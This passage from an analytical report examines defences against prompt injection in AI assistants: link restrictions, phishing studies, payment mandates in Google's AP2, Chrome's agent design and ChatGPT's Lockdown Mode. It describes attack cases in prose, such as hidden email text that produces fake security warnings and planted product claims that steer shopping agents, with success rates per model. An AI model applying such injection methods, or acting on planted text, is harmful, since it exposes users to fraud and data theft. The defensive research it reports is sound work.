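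Netcraft concludes that more than one in three users could end up at a site the brand doesn't own. The figures don't support this, because they count each domain once, no matter how often the models gave it. If 967 of 1,000 answers were correct and the 33 wrong ones each named a different domain, a third of the domains could be wrong but only 3.3% of the answers. Netcraft doesn't publish the share of wrong answers, and it sells services for finding and removing phishing sites.

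The test also dates from mid-2025. ThaiCERT's *Experts Warn of New Phishing Threats Using LLMs* (2025) relayed the results that July. Newer assistants that search the web before answering probably make up fewer addresses, but nobody appears to have published a repeat of the test on them.

### Linking only to pages the software has retrieved

A product can let the model link only to pages that the product's software has retrieved. For example, the model can refer to a source by number, and the software inserts the address it has on record. The model then cannot make up an address or add private data to one.

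This rule would also have removed the links in Permiso's demonstration if the developer had applied it strictly. ChatGPT's software had retrieved the page that the user wanted summarised, but not the phishing page that the planted text linked to. A looser rule that accepted every address found on a retrieved page would have allowed the attacker's link. Anthropic had to correct the same weakness in its rule for pages that Claude opens by itself.

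Even under the strict rule, a retrieved page may be dishonest. Netcraft found that Perplexity, an AI search engine, gave a phishing page as its top link in response to a question about logging in to the bank Wells Fargo. The page was public and imitated the bank convincingly. It was hosted on Google Sites, a free website builder, so even a list of trusted domains might have allowed it.

For login pages, a developer could use a much narrower rule. The assistant would show login links only from a list of verified addresses for banks, email services and government offices, and would not guess the address of an organisation that isn't on it. People who use a small credit union missing from the list would have to find its login page another way.

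### Showing the full address first

A link's visible text may have nothing to do with its destination. Some products therefore show the address and wait for the user to confirm, as ChatGPT does for unverified links. Embrace The Red reported in 2024 that Google Colab prefixed every clickable link with a Google address, which opened a confirmation page before the browser went on to the destination. Tenable later observed that Gemini also sent links through a Google address, but did not say whether users had to confirm them.

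Reading an address correctly is harder than it sounds, because the user has to pick out the domain, ignore familiar names elsewhere in the address, and know which domain the bank really uses. In the Perplexity case, the domain belonged to Google, which many people would find reassuring.

A password manager can make part of this comparison automatically. According to Permiso, it may warn the user when a site's domain doesn't match the expected login page. The warning doesn't depend on how the user reached the page, so it works the same for links in emails and links in answers. But it doesn't protect someone who types in a card number, or who opens the page on a phone without the password manager.

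The restrictions differ in which harmful links they stop:

| Restriction | Link with private data in its address | Made-up login address | Published phishing page |
|---|---|---|---|
| No clickable links | Leaks only if the user copies the address | Harmful only if the user copies it | Harmful only if the user copies the address |
| Removal of known bad links | Misses new sites | Misses sites that nobody has reported | Removed once someone has reported it |
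| Links only to retrieved pages | Blocked | Blocked | Allowed if a search returned it |
| Full address shown first | User has to notice the data | User has to know the right domain | User has to know the right domain |

For a general assistant, linking only to retrieved pages and removing known bad ones seems the best combination. It doesn't block new phishing pages that a search engine returns, but people who use ordinary search engines already face that risk. The value of the other two restrictions depends more on how well users recognise phishing.

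### How often people click phishing links

*Understanding the Efficacy of Phishing Training in Practice*, by Ho, Mirian and colleagues, is the largest recent study of this question. It analysed simulated phishing emails that UC San Diego Health, a medical centre in California, sent to 19,789 employees over eight months in 2023. Each employee received one email a month and failed the test if they clicked its link. The centre randomly assigned employees to five groups. Four groups saw different kinds of training material whenever they clicked, and the fifth saw only an error page.

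Training reduced the average failure rate by 1.7 percentage points. The content of the email mattered far more. About 1.8% of recipients clicked a link in a message about their Outlook password, compared with 30.8% for a message about holiday policy. In the first month, 9.7% of employees clicked a link, and by the eighth month, 56% had clicked at least once.

The effect was small partly because most people hardly looked at the training. More than half of the sessions lasted less than ten seconds. Employees who completed an interactive version were 19% less likely to click a later phishing link, but Ho and colleagues caution that these employees may already have been more careful. The centre's compulsory annual course made no detectable difference. Employees who had taken it in the past month failed about as often as those who were overdue.

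These results are strong evidence about people, because the study was large, randomised and set in a real workplace. The centre had also set its email system to let the simulated messages through, so filters did not affect the outcome. The results suggest that advice to check links carefully would protect few of an assistant's users, and that an attacker who can try repeatedly will eventually deceive many people, including some who avoided earlier attempts.

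Other trials have tested whether AI can write phishing emails. In *Devising and Detecting Phishing* (Heiding, Schneier and colleagues, 2023), the human-written emails followed persuasion guidelines called the V-Triad. The 2024 trial used an AI system that first researched each target online. In *Can AI Models be Jailbroken to Phish Elderly Victims?* (Heiding and Lermen, 2025), researchers sent AI-written emails to older volunteers in California.

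| Trial | Participants | Emails | Share who clicked |
|---|---|---|---|
| 2023 | 112 | Generic phishing | 19–28% |
| 2023 | | Written by GPT-4 | 30–44% |
| 2023 | | Written by people using the V-Triad | 69–79% |
| 2023 | | GPT-4 and the V-Triad combined | 43–81% |
| 2024 | 101 | Generic phishing | 12% |
| 2024 | | Written by human experts | 54% |
| 2024 | | Fully automated AI | 54% |
| 2024 | | AI with human help | 56% |
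| 2025 | 108 | Written by various AI models | 11% |

In the 2024 trial, automated emails did as well as those written by human experts, whereas emails written by GPT-4 alone had done worse than the experts' a year earlier. However, each group had only about 25 people, so a click rate of 54% is compatible with a true rate anywhere from about 35% to 72%. The trial therefore can't establish that AI and experts were equally good, but it does show that both did much better than the generic email.

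The 11% in 2025 doesn't mean that AI had become less persuasive. The participants were older, the emails were less personal, and no group received human-written emails for comparison. The volunteers also knew they were in a study about emails, which Heiding and Lermen think may have made them more cautious. The researchers sent 268 emails, and twelve people clicked.

More recent work has moved away from counting clicks. *Context-Aware Spear Phishing* (2026) asked people to rate AI-written phishing emails, citing serious ethical problems with sending them to real targets. Ratings measure whether a message looks plausible, but someone who rates an email as convincing might still not click its link.

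All of these trials used email, so their click rates don't apply directly to an assistant. Users might click a link in a summary more often, because they asked for the summary and the link can fit the task. The wide range of results at UC San Diego Health suggests that relevance matters a great deal. But users might click less often if the link is in an account alert, which looks out of place in the summary of an article.

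### Trials with an assistant that misleads its user

No published trial appears to have measured how often people click a phishing link in an answer from an assistant they trust. The closest evidence comes from Li and colleagues, who had 303 people use an AI agent for realistic tasks such as choosing a job candidate, answering email and planning a trip. Each person did three of nine tasks, and in every one an attack had already made the agent act against its user.

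Afterwards the researchers asked whether anything had seemed unusual. They counted both "yes" and "unsure" as noticing the attack.

| Warning | Attacks noticed |
|---|---|
| One disclaimer at the start | 8.6% |
| A reminder beside each answer | 20.0% |
| An alert that interrupted the task | 25.0% |

Among those who saw only the disclaimer, people with technical expertise did slightly worse than the rest (6.8% compared with 9.6%). Alerts helped most when the answer was easy to check. The interrupting alert raised the share who noticed from 9.8% to 50% in a web search task, but only from 9.3% to 15% in the email task.

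These figures support the view that people rarely catch a manipulated assistant, but they don't measure how often people click phishing links, because none of the nine tasks contained one. The closest task involved a coding agent that recommended a malicious software package. Some attacks also left few visible signs, so users who missed them weren't necessarily careless. Every task contained an attack, so the study didn't measure how often people would report something unusual about an honest answer.

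The comparison between warnings is less certain than the low overall rate. Li and colleagues report the sizes of the three groups inconsistently, as 101, 103 and 99 people in one place and as 183, 60 and 60 in another. The interrupting alert also appeared only when the agent's output was suspicious. A real product would have to detect the attack before showing the alert, and if it could do that reliably, it could block the answer instead.

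*I know it's not right, but that's what it said to do* (2025) describes a much smaller experiment, in which 15 people received security advice on subjects such as passwords and firewalls from both a good chatbot and a compromised one that gave deliberately bad advice. The title quotes a participant who apparently followed advice despite doubting it. The experiment can show that this happens, but it is too small to show how often.

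It is plausible that users trust an assistant's links more than an email's, but no one has measured this. Researchers could do so without much difficulty by putting the same harmless test link in an email for one group and in an assistant's summary of that email for another, then comparing the clicks. Heiding and Lermen's method would limit the risk, since it sent anyone who clicked straight to a page that explained the study.

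### A false warning with no link

An attacker can also deceive users without a link. According to Heiding and Lermen, a researcher named Figueroa reported in 2025 that hidden text in an email could make Gemini's summary of it in Gmail show a false security warning. Permiso had found a similar weakness in Microsoft Copilot's email summaries.

If such a warning tells the user to ring a telephone number, there is no link to remove, no address for Safe Browsing to check and no destination for the user to inspect. Once the user rings the number, the rest of the fraud happens by telephone, where the assistant's maker can't restrict anything. Making the number unclickable would hardly help, since people are used to dialling numbers themselves.

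Other restrictions could make this deception harder. A developer can give the model only the text that a reader of the email would see. This would remove hidden instructions without the developer having to recognise them, although it would also remove legitimate hidden text, such as image descriptions for blind readers. The software could also leave a telephone number out of a summary unless it appears in the visible part of the email. The user would lose very little, because they could still open the email and read it. An attacker could still put a false warning in the visible text, but the user could then see who sent it.

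Developers can also show genuine warnings outside the model's text. When Gemini blocks suspicious content in a document, Google displays a yellow banner with a link to its help pages. If every genuine warning appeared in such a banner, any warning inside a summary would be fake. But users would need to know this, and the training results from UC San Diego Health give little reason to expect that many would learn it from a help page.

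Conversation can also build trust over a longer period. *Love, Lies, and Language Models* (2025) studied romance scams by having participants exchange messages with a human and a language model for seven days. Participants trusted the model more. The researchers then tested whether participants would install an app that their partner suggested. When told that one partner was an AI, 20 of the 22 participants correctly identified it, but they had not acted on any suspicion before then. Because participants had believed they were talking to people, the study shows how persuasive a model can be, but not how much people trust an assistant.

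A chatbot can also get people to disclose information by asking. *Malicious LLM-Based Conversational AI Makes Users Reveal Personal Information* (2025) compared several styles of malicious chatbot. Those that offered something in return, such as sympathy or a story of their own, obtained less personal data, but more of it was true. In that study, the chatbot's operator was the attacker and received the answers directly. An outsider who manipulated someone else's assistant would still need a way to retrieve them, so restrictions on images, links and web addresses would remain useful.

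These restrictions would not help if the attacker's goal was the false statement itself, as with the slanted recommendation of a flat. Protection then depends on the model resisting the planted text and on the user checking the original.

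## Payments and purchases

If an agent can pay by itself, an attacker who wants the user's money doesn't need the user to click anything. But a payment is in some ways easier to contain than a data leak. The harm from a leaked inbox can't be predicted or the data taken back, whereas software can cap a payment, and the user can sometimes recover the money by returning the product or disputing the charge. Cards usually come with a dispute process, but the websites that Zscaler found in July 2026 tried to make agents pay in cryptocurrency, and those payments are usually final.

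Payments are harder to restrict than image loading. An agent can do most office work without loading images, but users often want their agents to spend money, for example to buy a train ticket. Unwanted purchases can also happen without an attacker. When Visa connected its payment network to ChatGPT in June 2026, Fortune (2026) reported that banks and retailers worried that customers might overspend, that agents might buy the wrong item, and that customers might deny having authorised a purchase.

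### What current products allow

The strictest restriction blocks an agent from financial sites. A looser one lets the agent shop but requires the user to make or approve the payment. The loosest lets the agent pay without asking if the amount is under a spending limit or the payee is permitted.

Anthropic has tightened the restrictions on purchases in Claude in Chrome, its browser agent, but seems to have loosened those on financial sites. During the pilot, users had to confirm purchases and Claude could not visit financial sites, according to eWeek's *Claude-for-Chrome Pilot*. By August 2026, Anthropic's *Claude in Chrome permissions guide* listed purchases and financial transactions among the actions that Claude may not take, whatever permissions the user has given. In September, a troubleshooting page from Anthropic still listed banks and investment platforms as blocked by default, but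 by November Anthropic's *Use Claude in Chrome safely* said that Claude asks for permission before opening financial sites.

The November page doesn't mention ordinary purchases in its own list of prohibited actions, and it says users remain responsible for any purchases Claude makes. But it refers readers to the permissions guide, so the ban is probably still in force.

Anthropic doesn't explain how it enforces the ban on purchases. The same list forbids Claude to carry out instructions from emails or web pages. No fixed rule could reliably recognise such instructions, so at least part of the list must depend on a model's judgement. If the ban on purchases does too, Claude is still able to buy things and might do so if manipulated.

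OpenAI says that ChatGPT agent, which operates websites for the user, asks for confirmation before high-impact actions and has a "watch mode" that requires the user to supervise it on certain sites. Through a connection with Visa, ChatGPT can also complete purchases, potentially at any business that accepts Visa, according to Global News' *ChatGPT can now shop and pay on behalf of customers* (2026). Visa's earlier attempts to work with AI platforms covered only a single merchant or a group of enrolled ones, which in effect limited agents to a list of approved payees. The new arrangement drops that limit. Fortune reported spending limits and approvals as its safeguards. Users can also turn on Lockdown Mode, which removes shopping and finance features.

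Google's agent in Chrome either asks for permission before a purchase or has the user complete it.

| Restriction | What the agent can still do | Where it applies |
|---|---|---|
| Financial sites blocked | Shop elsewhere | Claude in Chrome during its pilot |
| Purchases banned | Find and compare products | Claude in Chrome, August 2026 |
| User completes the payment | Fill the cart | Chrome, for some purchases |
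| User confirms the payment | Pay after approval | Chrome, for other purchases; ChatGPT agent, for high-impact actions |
| Spending limit | Pay within the limit | ChatGPT with Visa, alongside approvals |

### Google's design for Chrome

Chrome's agent works in the user's browser, where the user may be logged in to a bank, shops and an email account. *Architecting Security for Agentic Capabilities in Chrome* (Parker, 2025) describes in unusual detail how Google tries to keep a manipulated agent from misusing that access.

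A Gemini model called the planner reads web pages and chooses each action. Google trains it to resist known attacks and uses techniques that steer it to follow the user's instructions over those on a page. But Google assumes these measures will sometimes fail.

A separate Gemini model, the User Alignment Critic, checks whether each action serves the user's stated goal before Chrome carries it out. The critic receives only a description of the action, never the unfiltered page, so an attacker can't address it directly through text on a website. When the critic rejects an action, the planner gets feedback and tries again. After repeated failures, the planner can return control to the user.

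If a user asks for a T-shirt and planted text causes the planner to open the user's email, the critic should detect that this has nothing to do with T-shirts. If the text causes the planner to choose an overpriced T-shirt, the critic will probably approve, because adding a T-shirt to the cart is what the user asked for. Parker acknowledges that the critic has less context than the planner, though its job is simpler. The critic is still a model and can make mistakes, but an attacker has much less influence over what it reads.

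Chrome also limits which sites the agent can use. Browsers already stop a page on one site from reading the user's data on another, but an agent that moves freely between sites could undo this protection by carrying data across. To prevent this, Google's Agent Origin Sets feature (an origin is roughly one website) keeps two lists of sites for each session. The agent may read sites on the read-only list, and it may also click and type on sites on the read-writable list. Parker gives the example of an agent that collects ingredients from a recipe site and fills a shopping cart on a grocer's site. Only the grocer's site would need to be read-writable.

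A piece of code, which Parker calls a gating function, decides which sites are relevant to the task without access to any untrusted web content. If a page embeds a frame from an unlisted site, such as an advertisement, Chrome doesn't show that frame to the model. A version of the critic must approve any new site before the planner visits it or a page redirects there by itself. A fixed rule, much like OpenAI's check, also requires any address the model writes to be a known public one. Google applies a similar distinction between reading and writing to the agent's other tools.

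For purchases, the read-writable list works somewhat like a list of permitted shops. A planted comment on the recipe site couldn't make the agent buy from an unrelated shop unless the software accepted that shop as relevant. Chrome enforces the list in code, but a model helps choose which sites are on it, so the list is less predictable than one a person has written.

Google had not built all of this when it published the design in December 2025. The first version tracked only the read-writable sites, so it did not distinguish between reading and acting. Parker said Google wanted to see how the limits affected real tasks before adjusting them.

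The last part of the design is confirmation, which Chrome requires in several situations:

- Before the agent opens a sensitive site, such as a bank or a site with medical records, Chrome asks the user. It identifies these sites from a fixed list.
- Before the agent signs in to a site with Google Password Manager, Chrome asks again. The model has no direct access to the stored passwords.
- Before a purchase, a payment or a message, the agent "will try to pause" and either ask for permission or have the user take over.

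The word "try" suggests that Chrome has to recognise a purchase before it can ask about it. Parker compares this step to Google's other safety classifiers and says the company is working on unusual cases. The check on bank sites is more dependable because it needs only a list. A manipulated agent is therefore more likely to complete an odd-looking checkout at a shop than to reach the user's bank unnoticed.

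Chrome also runs a classifier on every page to look for planted instructions, and shows the user a log of the agent's steps. Google tests its agent against automatically generated malicious sites and offers outside researchers up to $20,000 for serious breaches. Parker gives no success rates for these attacks, so outsiders can judge the design but not how well it works.

### How the Agent Payments Protocol works

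Chrome's confirmations protect people who use Chrome, but a shop that receives an order from another agent can't tell whether the user approved it. The *Agent Payments Protocol Documentation* explains that existing payment systems assume a person is clicking "buy" on a trusted website. Google introduced the protocol, known as AP2, in September 2025 to give shops and payment companies proof of what the user had authorised. Version 0.2 followed in April 2026, and work on the standard now continues at the FIDO Alliance, an industry group known for its login standards.

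In AP2, the proof of a user's authorisation is a digitally signed record called a mandate. The signature lets anyone check which key signed the record and whether the record has changed since. A checkout mandate covers what the user is buying, and a payment mandate covers how the user is paying.

AP2's *Agentic Payment Protocol (v0.2)* divides the work of a purchase among a shopping agent, a merchant, the merchant's payment processor, a credential provider (which holds the user's payment methods, as a digital wallet does) and a "trusted surface". The trusted surface is the screen on which the user reviews and approves the purchase. It must not use a language model, because a model could misrepresent what the user is about to sign.

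When the user is present, a purchase goes as follows, according to AP2's *Flow Examples*:

1. The agent puts together a cart with the merchant, and the merchant signs the resulting checkout.
2. The agent chooses one of the payment methods that the credential provider offers.
3. The trusted surface shows the user the purchase, confirms the user's identity, for instance with a fingerprint, and signs both mandates.
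4. The agent sends the payment mandate to the credential provider, which checks it and issues a token for the payment.
5. The agent sends the token and the checkout mandate to the merchant. The merchant compares the mandate with the current cart and starts the payment.
6. The payment processor checks that the token belongs to this checkout. The merchant and the processor then issue signed receipts.

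Both mandates contain the same hash, a short code computed from the signed checkout. If someone changes the price or swaps an item after the user approves the purchase, the hash no longer matches and the payment fails. An attacker who steals a payment mandate also can't use it for a different order.

If the user won't be present to approve a particular cart, they sign "open" mandates in advance, which set limits on the purchase. One of AP2's examples is an instruction to buy a pair of shoes once the price falls below 100 dollars. When the agent finds a suitable offer, it signs "closed" mandates for that purchase with its own key and sends them along with the open ones. The open mandates name the agent's key, so another program can't use them.

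| | Checkout mandate | Payment mandate |
|---|---|---|
| What the closed form fixes | The merchant's signed checkout, including the products | The payee, amount, payment method and associated checkout |
| Limits the open form can set | Permitted merchants, products and quantities | Price range, payees, payment methods, dates, repeat payments and total budget |
| Who checks it | The merchant | The credential provider, payment network and payment processor |

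Ordinary code has to perform these checks, even if a company uses a language model for everything else. For example, the price rule in AP2's *Payment Mandate* compares the payment with a minimum and a maximum in a stated currency. If the limits leave something unclear, the merchant or the credential provider can bring the user back to approve the purchase directly.

AP2 relies on the merchant to check that the products are permitted, but a dishonest merchant would have no reason to reject its own sale. The payment companies would still enforce the permitted amount and payee, and the signed records would help the user prove the violation afterwards. AP2 also protects only purchases that use it. The Universal Commerce Protocol (UCP), a shopping standard that works with AP2, activates the mandates only if both the merchant and the agent's platform support them.

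AP2's *Security and Privacy Considerations* assumes that preventing prompt injection is infeasible and treats every model and agent as a potential attacker. Like capability restrictions in general, the mandates' limits are meant to contain the damage when manipulation succeeds, keeping the worst-case loss "strictly bounded" if planted text leads an agent to make a bad purchase.

### What a 50-dollar limit prevents

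Suppose a user asks an agent to buy a replacement filter for a water jug while they are at work. They sign open mandates that allow one purchase of up to 50 dollars from either of two shops. The right filter costs 30 dollars. An attacker then uses planted text to control the agent's choice.

| What the agent tries to buy | Result |
|---|---|
| A 400-dollar phone from a permitted shop | Rejected, because it exceeds the limit |
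| A 45-dollar filter from an unknown seller | Rejected, because the seller is not a permitted payee |
| The wrong filter, for 49 dollars, from a permitted shop | Accepted |

The limits cap what could have been a large theft at 50 dollars. If the 49-dollar filter fits the jug after all, the user has overpaid by 19 dollars. If it doesn't fit and the shop won't take it back, they have lost the full 49.

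This bound assumes that the agent can use the mandate only once. Under AP2, agents are not supposed to attempt a second purchase until the first has failed, but a manipulated agent might do so anyway. Payment companies may reject overlapping purchases, though AP2 doesn't require them to. For repeat orders, the user can also set a total budget. Without one, a mandate for monthly purchases of up to 50 dollars would allow 600 dollars of spending in a year.

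The user could also have specified the exact product. AP2's *Checkout Mandate* includes a rule that lists acceptable items by identification number, which would have blocked the purchase of the wrong filter. But someone has to find the right number before the user signs. A user who looks it up has done much of the agent's work. If the agent looks it up instead, an attacker can influence it at that stage, and the user has to notice the mistake on the approval screen.

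The user could find it harder to get the money back than after ordinary card fraud. The mandates would show that the user had authorised a purchase of this size from this shop, and the purchase kept to those terms. If the agent had exceeded the limit, the same records would have helped the user. AP2 leaves others to decide how such evidence should count in a dispute.

A spending limit also restricts each purchase more than it restricts what an attacker can earn across many users. If 10,000 users' agents were manipulated into buying the same $49 filter, the seller would take in $490,000, and many of the buyers might not complain about so small a loss.

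### Three studies of AP2

In three 2026 studies, researchers attacked AP2 and concluded that its signatures protect the transaction but not the choice that led to it, as the example of the wrong filter illustrates.

*Whispers of Wealth* (Debi, Zhu and Sen Gupta, 2026) reports 30 trials of a shopping agent that used the first version of AP2 and Gemini 2.5 Flash. The user always asked for outdoor basketball shoes. In ten ordinary trials, the agent recommended suitable products. In ten others, one product's description contained planted instructions, and the agent ranked that product first every time. Six of those rankings clearly contradicted the user's request. In the last ten trials, a malicious user tried to obtain another customer's details and succeeded twice. The mandates remained valid throughout.

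This was a small test of one task and one model. Two successes in ten trials are compatible with a true rate from about 3% to 56%. Ranking a product first also didn't complete a purchase, because the user still had to approve the cart. Debi and colleagues didn't test how many people would have objected.

Aviv, Gandh and colleagues (2026) examined version 0.2 more systematically in *Beyond the Mandate*. They divided a transaction into five phases and considered five ways a company might set up its agents and tools, such as a marketplace that represents many sellers. They identified 48 threats and rated eight as high risk in at least one setup. Because no complete public deployment of AP2 existed, they built their own test system and demonstrated all eight there, along with repairs.

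In one demonstration, a user who wanted to spend no more than 50 dollars on a camera ended up approving a mandate that allowed up to 80 dollars and any payee. Every signature was valid and the mandate's limits were enforced, but they weren't the limits the user wanted. Aviv and colleagues recommend that the trusted surface show the exact maximum, point out when there is no payee restriction, and reject any maximum above the one the user originally gave. Other demonstrations exploited shared platforms that confused one company's requests or data with another's. The repairs for these tie each request to a verified sender.

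The count of eight depends heavily on the scoring. Aviv and colleagues averaged a standard severity score with a score for features of AI agents, then multiplied the result by 0.97. One threat scored 8.3 and 6.5, for a final score of 7.2, just above the high-risk threshold of 7.0. They also scored the threats as if the company had no defences. A developer can use the scores to decide what to fix first, but they don't show how likely an attack is.

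In *Signing the Transaction but Not the Decision*, Louck, Dvir and Stulman (2026) report the largest set of experiments. They planted text in product descriptions to test the sample shopping agent that AP2's maintainers publish for purchases with the user present.

| What the planted text changed | Model | Attempts | Success rate |
|---|---|---|---|
| Whose payment details the agent looked up | Gemini 2.5 Flash-Lite | 50 | 90% |
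| The contents of the signed cart | Gemini 2.5 Flash-Lite | 50 | 56% |
| Which of the displayed products the agent recommended | Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite | 90 | 73.3% |

These rates are close to a worst case. The models are small and cheap, and the first two rates come from the last of three rounds in which the researchers improved the wording. In the first round, those two rates were 32% and 14%.

The result for product choice is the most troubling because the planted text made a false claim about the products instead of giving an instruction, and the agent drew the conclusion the attacker wanted. Training a model to ignore outside instructions doesn't prepare it for this. Larger models were not reliably safer. The attack succeeded 67.1% of the time against a preview of Gemini 3.1 Pro and 41.1% against GPT-5.5. It succeeded only 1.2% of the time against Claude Opus 5, often because the model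 checked the claim with the merchant first. A model can therefore learn to resist this kind of deception, but a shop or payment company can't control which model a customer's agent uses.

Louck and colleagues also tested Google's consumer assistant. It rejected a false claim in all eight trials when they pasted the claim into the chat, but accepted the same claim in all twelve trials when it read it on a web page. This suggests that Google's safeguards covered what users typed but not what the assistant retrieved, which would include a dishonest seller's text. In these trials, the assistant recommended products but didn't buy them.

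The sample agent for purchases with the user present sets no spending limit or payee list, since the user approves the final cart. A second sample agent, for purchases in the user's absence, sets both. Louck and colleagues applied these two limits to manipulated purchases that they had collected from 27 models:

| Effect of the manipulation | Cases | Result with the limits |
|---|---|---|
| Payment went to the wrong payee | 634 | The payee list blocked all of them |
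| Price rose above the displayed one | 534 | A cap at the displayed price blocked all of them |
| Cart contained an extra item at the same total | 597 | The cap blocked none of them |
| Agent chose a more expensive product | 567 | A tight cap blocked all of them, but a generous budget did not |

This is the best available evidence on how well such limits work. The limits blocked every change they covered, whichever model had made the mistake. They did not stop the agent from choosing a worse product within the budget, as with the 49-dollar filter.

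### Checking the purchase against what the user saw

Louck and colleagues propose a defence called A-VIP, which adds further fixed checks to AP2. Its rules address each kind of manipulation separately.

A-VIP protects payment details by preventing the agent from choosing which account to use. In the sample system, the agent told the credential provider whose payment methods to look up, so a manipulated agent could name someone else. The lookup happened before any mandate existed, so no mandate could limit it. Under A-VIP, the provider identifies the account from the user's login and issues a single-use token tied to one cart and one merchant.

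To protect the cart, A-VIP records each product and price when the agent displays them. It later rejects any cart with an item that wasn't displayed, a price that differs from the one displayed, too large a quantity or a total that doesn't add up. It also rejects payment to anyone except the merchant that offered the product. In the researchers' tests, these fixed checks blocked forged lookups and forged carts without rejecting any legitimate purchases.

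A-VIP also includes a text scanner, which did much worse. It wrongly flagged 12% of legitimate cases in a demanding test. Planted instructions that language models had rewritten to avoid detection got past the scanner in 79% of the cart attacks and 17% of the lookup attacks. Louck and colleagues therefore treat the scanner as a secondary layer.

Neither the payment-detail check nor the cart checks can detect a manipulated choice, because the agent buys a real product at its real price. In one test, the cart checks accepted all 68 such purchases. A-VIP therefore requires the user's approval if the user hasn't set a budget and the agent picks something more expensive than the cheapest product that meets the request. This rule flagged all 68 purchases, but that result was almost guaranteed because every promoted product in the test cost more than the alternative.

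The rule also interrupts people who have good reasons to pay more. Louck and colleagues tested it on 24 legitimate requests where the more expensive product was the right choice. It triggered a confirmation prompt for all 16 requests without a stated budget and for none of the 8 with one. They conclude that users can avoid the extra prompts by stating a budget, without losing protection.

That seems too optimistic. If a stated budget turns off the prompt, a manipulated agent can choose any product within the budget without the user hearing about it. The water filter buyer had set a $50 limit, so A-VIP would have let the $49 filter through. A budget protects users well only if it is close to the price of the right product, and people who delegate their shopping often don't know that price. Without a budget, protection depends on users reading each prompt instead of clicking through it. The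 rule also misses a bad product if it is the cheapest on offer.

A-VIP's other checks seem clearly worth adopting, since they did not hinder legitimate buyers in the tests and they run without a language model. Google accepted the payment lookup flaw as a bug of moderate severity and assigned an engineer to it, but the flaw was still in the sample system when Louck and colleagues wrote their paper in September 2026. Google was also still reviewing their findings on manipulated product choices.

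## Withholding many capabilities for a session or a task

Restricting one capability often leaves a manipulated model with others it can misuse. For example, an assistant that can't load outside images may still be able to open pages, and one that can open only public addresses may still be able to send email. Some developers therefore withhold many capabilities at once, either for a whole session or for a single task that doesn't need them.

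The danger arises when one session combines private data, untrusted content and the ability to take actions that affect the outside world. Suppose a user asks an assistant to summarise a web page and then, in the same conversation, to find a figure in their tax return and email it to an accountant. The page is still in the context when the assistant opens the tax return and uses the email account, so instructions planted in the page could affect the second task. Starting a new session for the second task would keep those instructions out of its context.

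### ChatGPT's Lockdown Mode

Lockdown Mode is an optional setting that turns off or limits most of the ways ChatGPT can contact the outside world. In February 2026, OpenAI announced it for organisations such as companies, schools and healthcare providers, in *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT*. In June, OpenAI extended the setting to personal accounts, including free ones, according to The Next Web's *OpenAI adds Lockdown Mode to ChatGPT to block data theft*.

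Besides the limits on images described earlier, the mode has these effects:

| Capability | In Lockdown Mode |
|---|---|
| Web browsing | Works only with stored copies of pages |
| Deep research, which writes long reports from many sources | Off |
| Agent mode, which operates websites | Off |
| Code that ChatGPT writes in Canvas, its editor | Can't use the network, even with the user's approval |
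| Downloading files to analyse | Off |
| Live connections to other services | Mostly blocked on personal accounts; administrators decide in managed workspaces |
| Uploading files, memory, image generation | Unchanged |
| Network access in Codex, OpenAI's coding agent | Unchanged |

OpenAI calls these limits deterministic, and Microsoft describes its blocks on images the same way. OpenAI turned off the features it couldn't make safe with such limits.

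When ChatGPT uses stored pages, it reads copies that OpenAI already holds, so no request reaches the website while the user is working. This is stricter than OpenAI's usual check on web addresses, which still lets a little information leak through the agent's choice of pages. However, a stored page may be out of date or missing. A user reading about the history of a treaty would hardly notice, but one asking whether a train is running late would get no useful answer.

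Data theft requires private data, planted instructions, and a way to send the data out. Lockdown Mode blocks only the last of these. Uploaded files and memory can still hold private data, and stored pages and uploaded files can still contain planted instructions. A manipulated model can therefore still give a wrong answer, as OpenAI acknowledges.

OpenAI promises only to "substantially reduce" the risk of data theft. It warns that data could still leak through apps that remain enabled, unforeseen combinations of features, or new techniques. Neither its announcement nor its help page gives leak rates with and without the mode.

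In February, OpenAI described the intended users as a small group, such as executives and security teams at prominent organisations, and said most people didn't need the mode. By June it was also recommending the mode for times when users are willing to give up some features for stricter protection. Users can turn it off for a single chat, which suits someone who handles confidential documents and later wants to plan a holiday. But the mode doesn't change memory, so the holiday chat may still have access to private details from other conversations.

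Turning on either Lockdown Mode or ChatGPT's Developer Mode turns off the other. Codex is a more important exception, because programmers often use it with private code. It has its own network settings, including a list of permitted domains and limits on the types of request it can make. Lockdown Mode doesn't protect users in Codex if they give it full internet access.

For settings like that one, OpenAI introduced "Elevated Risk" labels alongside Lockdown Mode. The labels mark certain features in ChatGPT, Codex and the Atlas browser whose risks the industry hasn't fully addressed. In Codex, the settings page explains what changes when network access is turned on, what could go wrong and when it is appropriate. OpenAI plans to remove a label once it considers the feature safe enough for general use. The labels don't restrict anything themselves, so they help only users who read and act on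 them.

### Which apps to leave on

In a managed workspace, such as a company's ChatGPT account, Lockdown Mode doesn't automatically turn off connected apps. Administrators choose which apps, and which actions within them, people may still use. OpenAI's help page grades the choices by risk:

| Action | Risk |
|---|---|
| Reading or writing through an app that the organisation doesn't trust | High |
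| Writing through a trusted app when outsiders might see the result | High |
| Writing through a trusted app when only trusted people can see the result | Medium |
| Reading through a trusted app | Medium |
| Searching an index of the organisation's documents | Medium |

OpenAI's guidance has no low-risk rating. OpenAI considers reading less risky than writing because reading changes nothing that an outsider could observe, but reading can still give a manipulated model data to steal.

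The risk grade of a write action depends on who can see the result. A comment on an internal support ticket might be medium risk, while the same comment on a ticket shared with a supplier would be high risk. An administrator therefore has to know how each team shares its files and tickets, and those arrangements change. Two companies that both use Lockdown Mode could get very different levels of protection.

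### Meta's Rule of Two

Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) offers developers a more general test. Until models can reliably detect and refuse prompt injection, Meta says, an agent should have no more than two of these properties within a session:

- It can process untrustworthy input.
- It can access sensitive systems or private data.
- It can change state or communicate externally.

Changing state means altering something that lasts, for example by deleting a file or making a payment. A person or some other reliable check should supervise any agent that needs all three properties.

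Meta adapted the rule from one that Google's Chromium browser project had used since 2019. Chromium's developers may combine no more than two of three things: untrustworthy input, an unsafe programming language and high privilege (Willison, 2025, in *Chromium Docs*).

Meta's example of an agent that breaks the rule is Email-Bot, an imaginary assistant that reads messages from anyone, searches the user's inbox and sends replies. Meta suggests three ways to fix it. The bot could read only messages from trusted senders, work in a test environment with no real data, or send messages only to trusted recipients or after a person checks the draft. The test environment would defeat the purpose of an email assistant, and the limit on senders would exclude most new correspondence, so for most people the only practical fix is to restrict sending.

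A web research assistant can comply without supervision. Meta's version opens any web address and fills in forms. But its browser runs in a sandbox where the user isn't logged in to anything, and it receives little private information beyond the request, so an attacker who took control of it would find almost nothing to steal.

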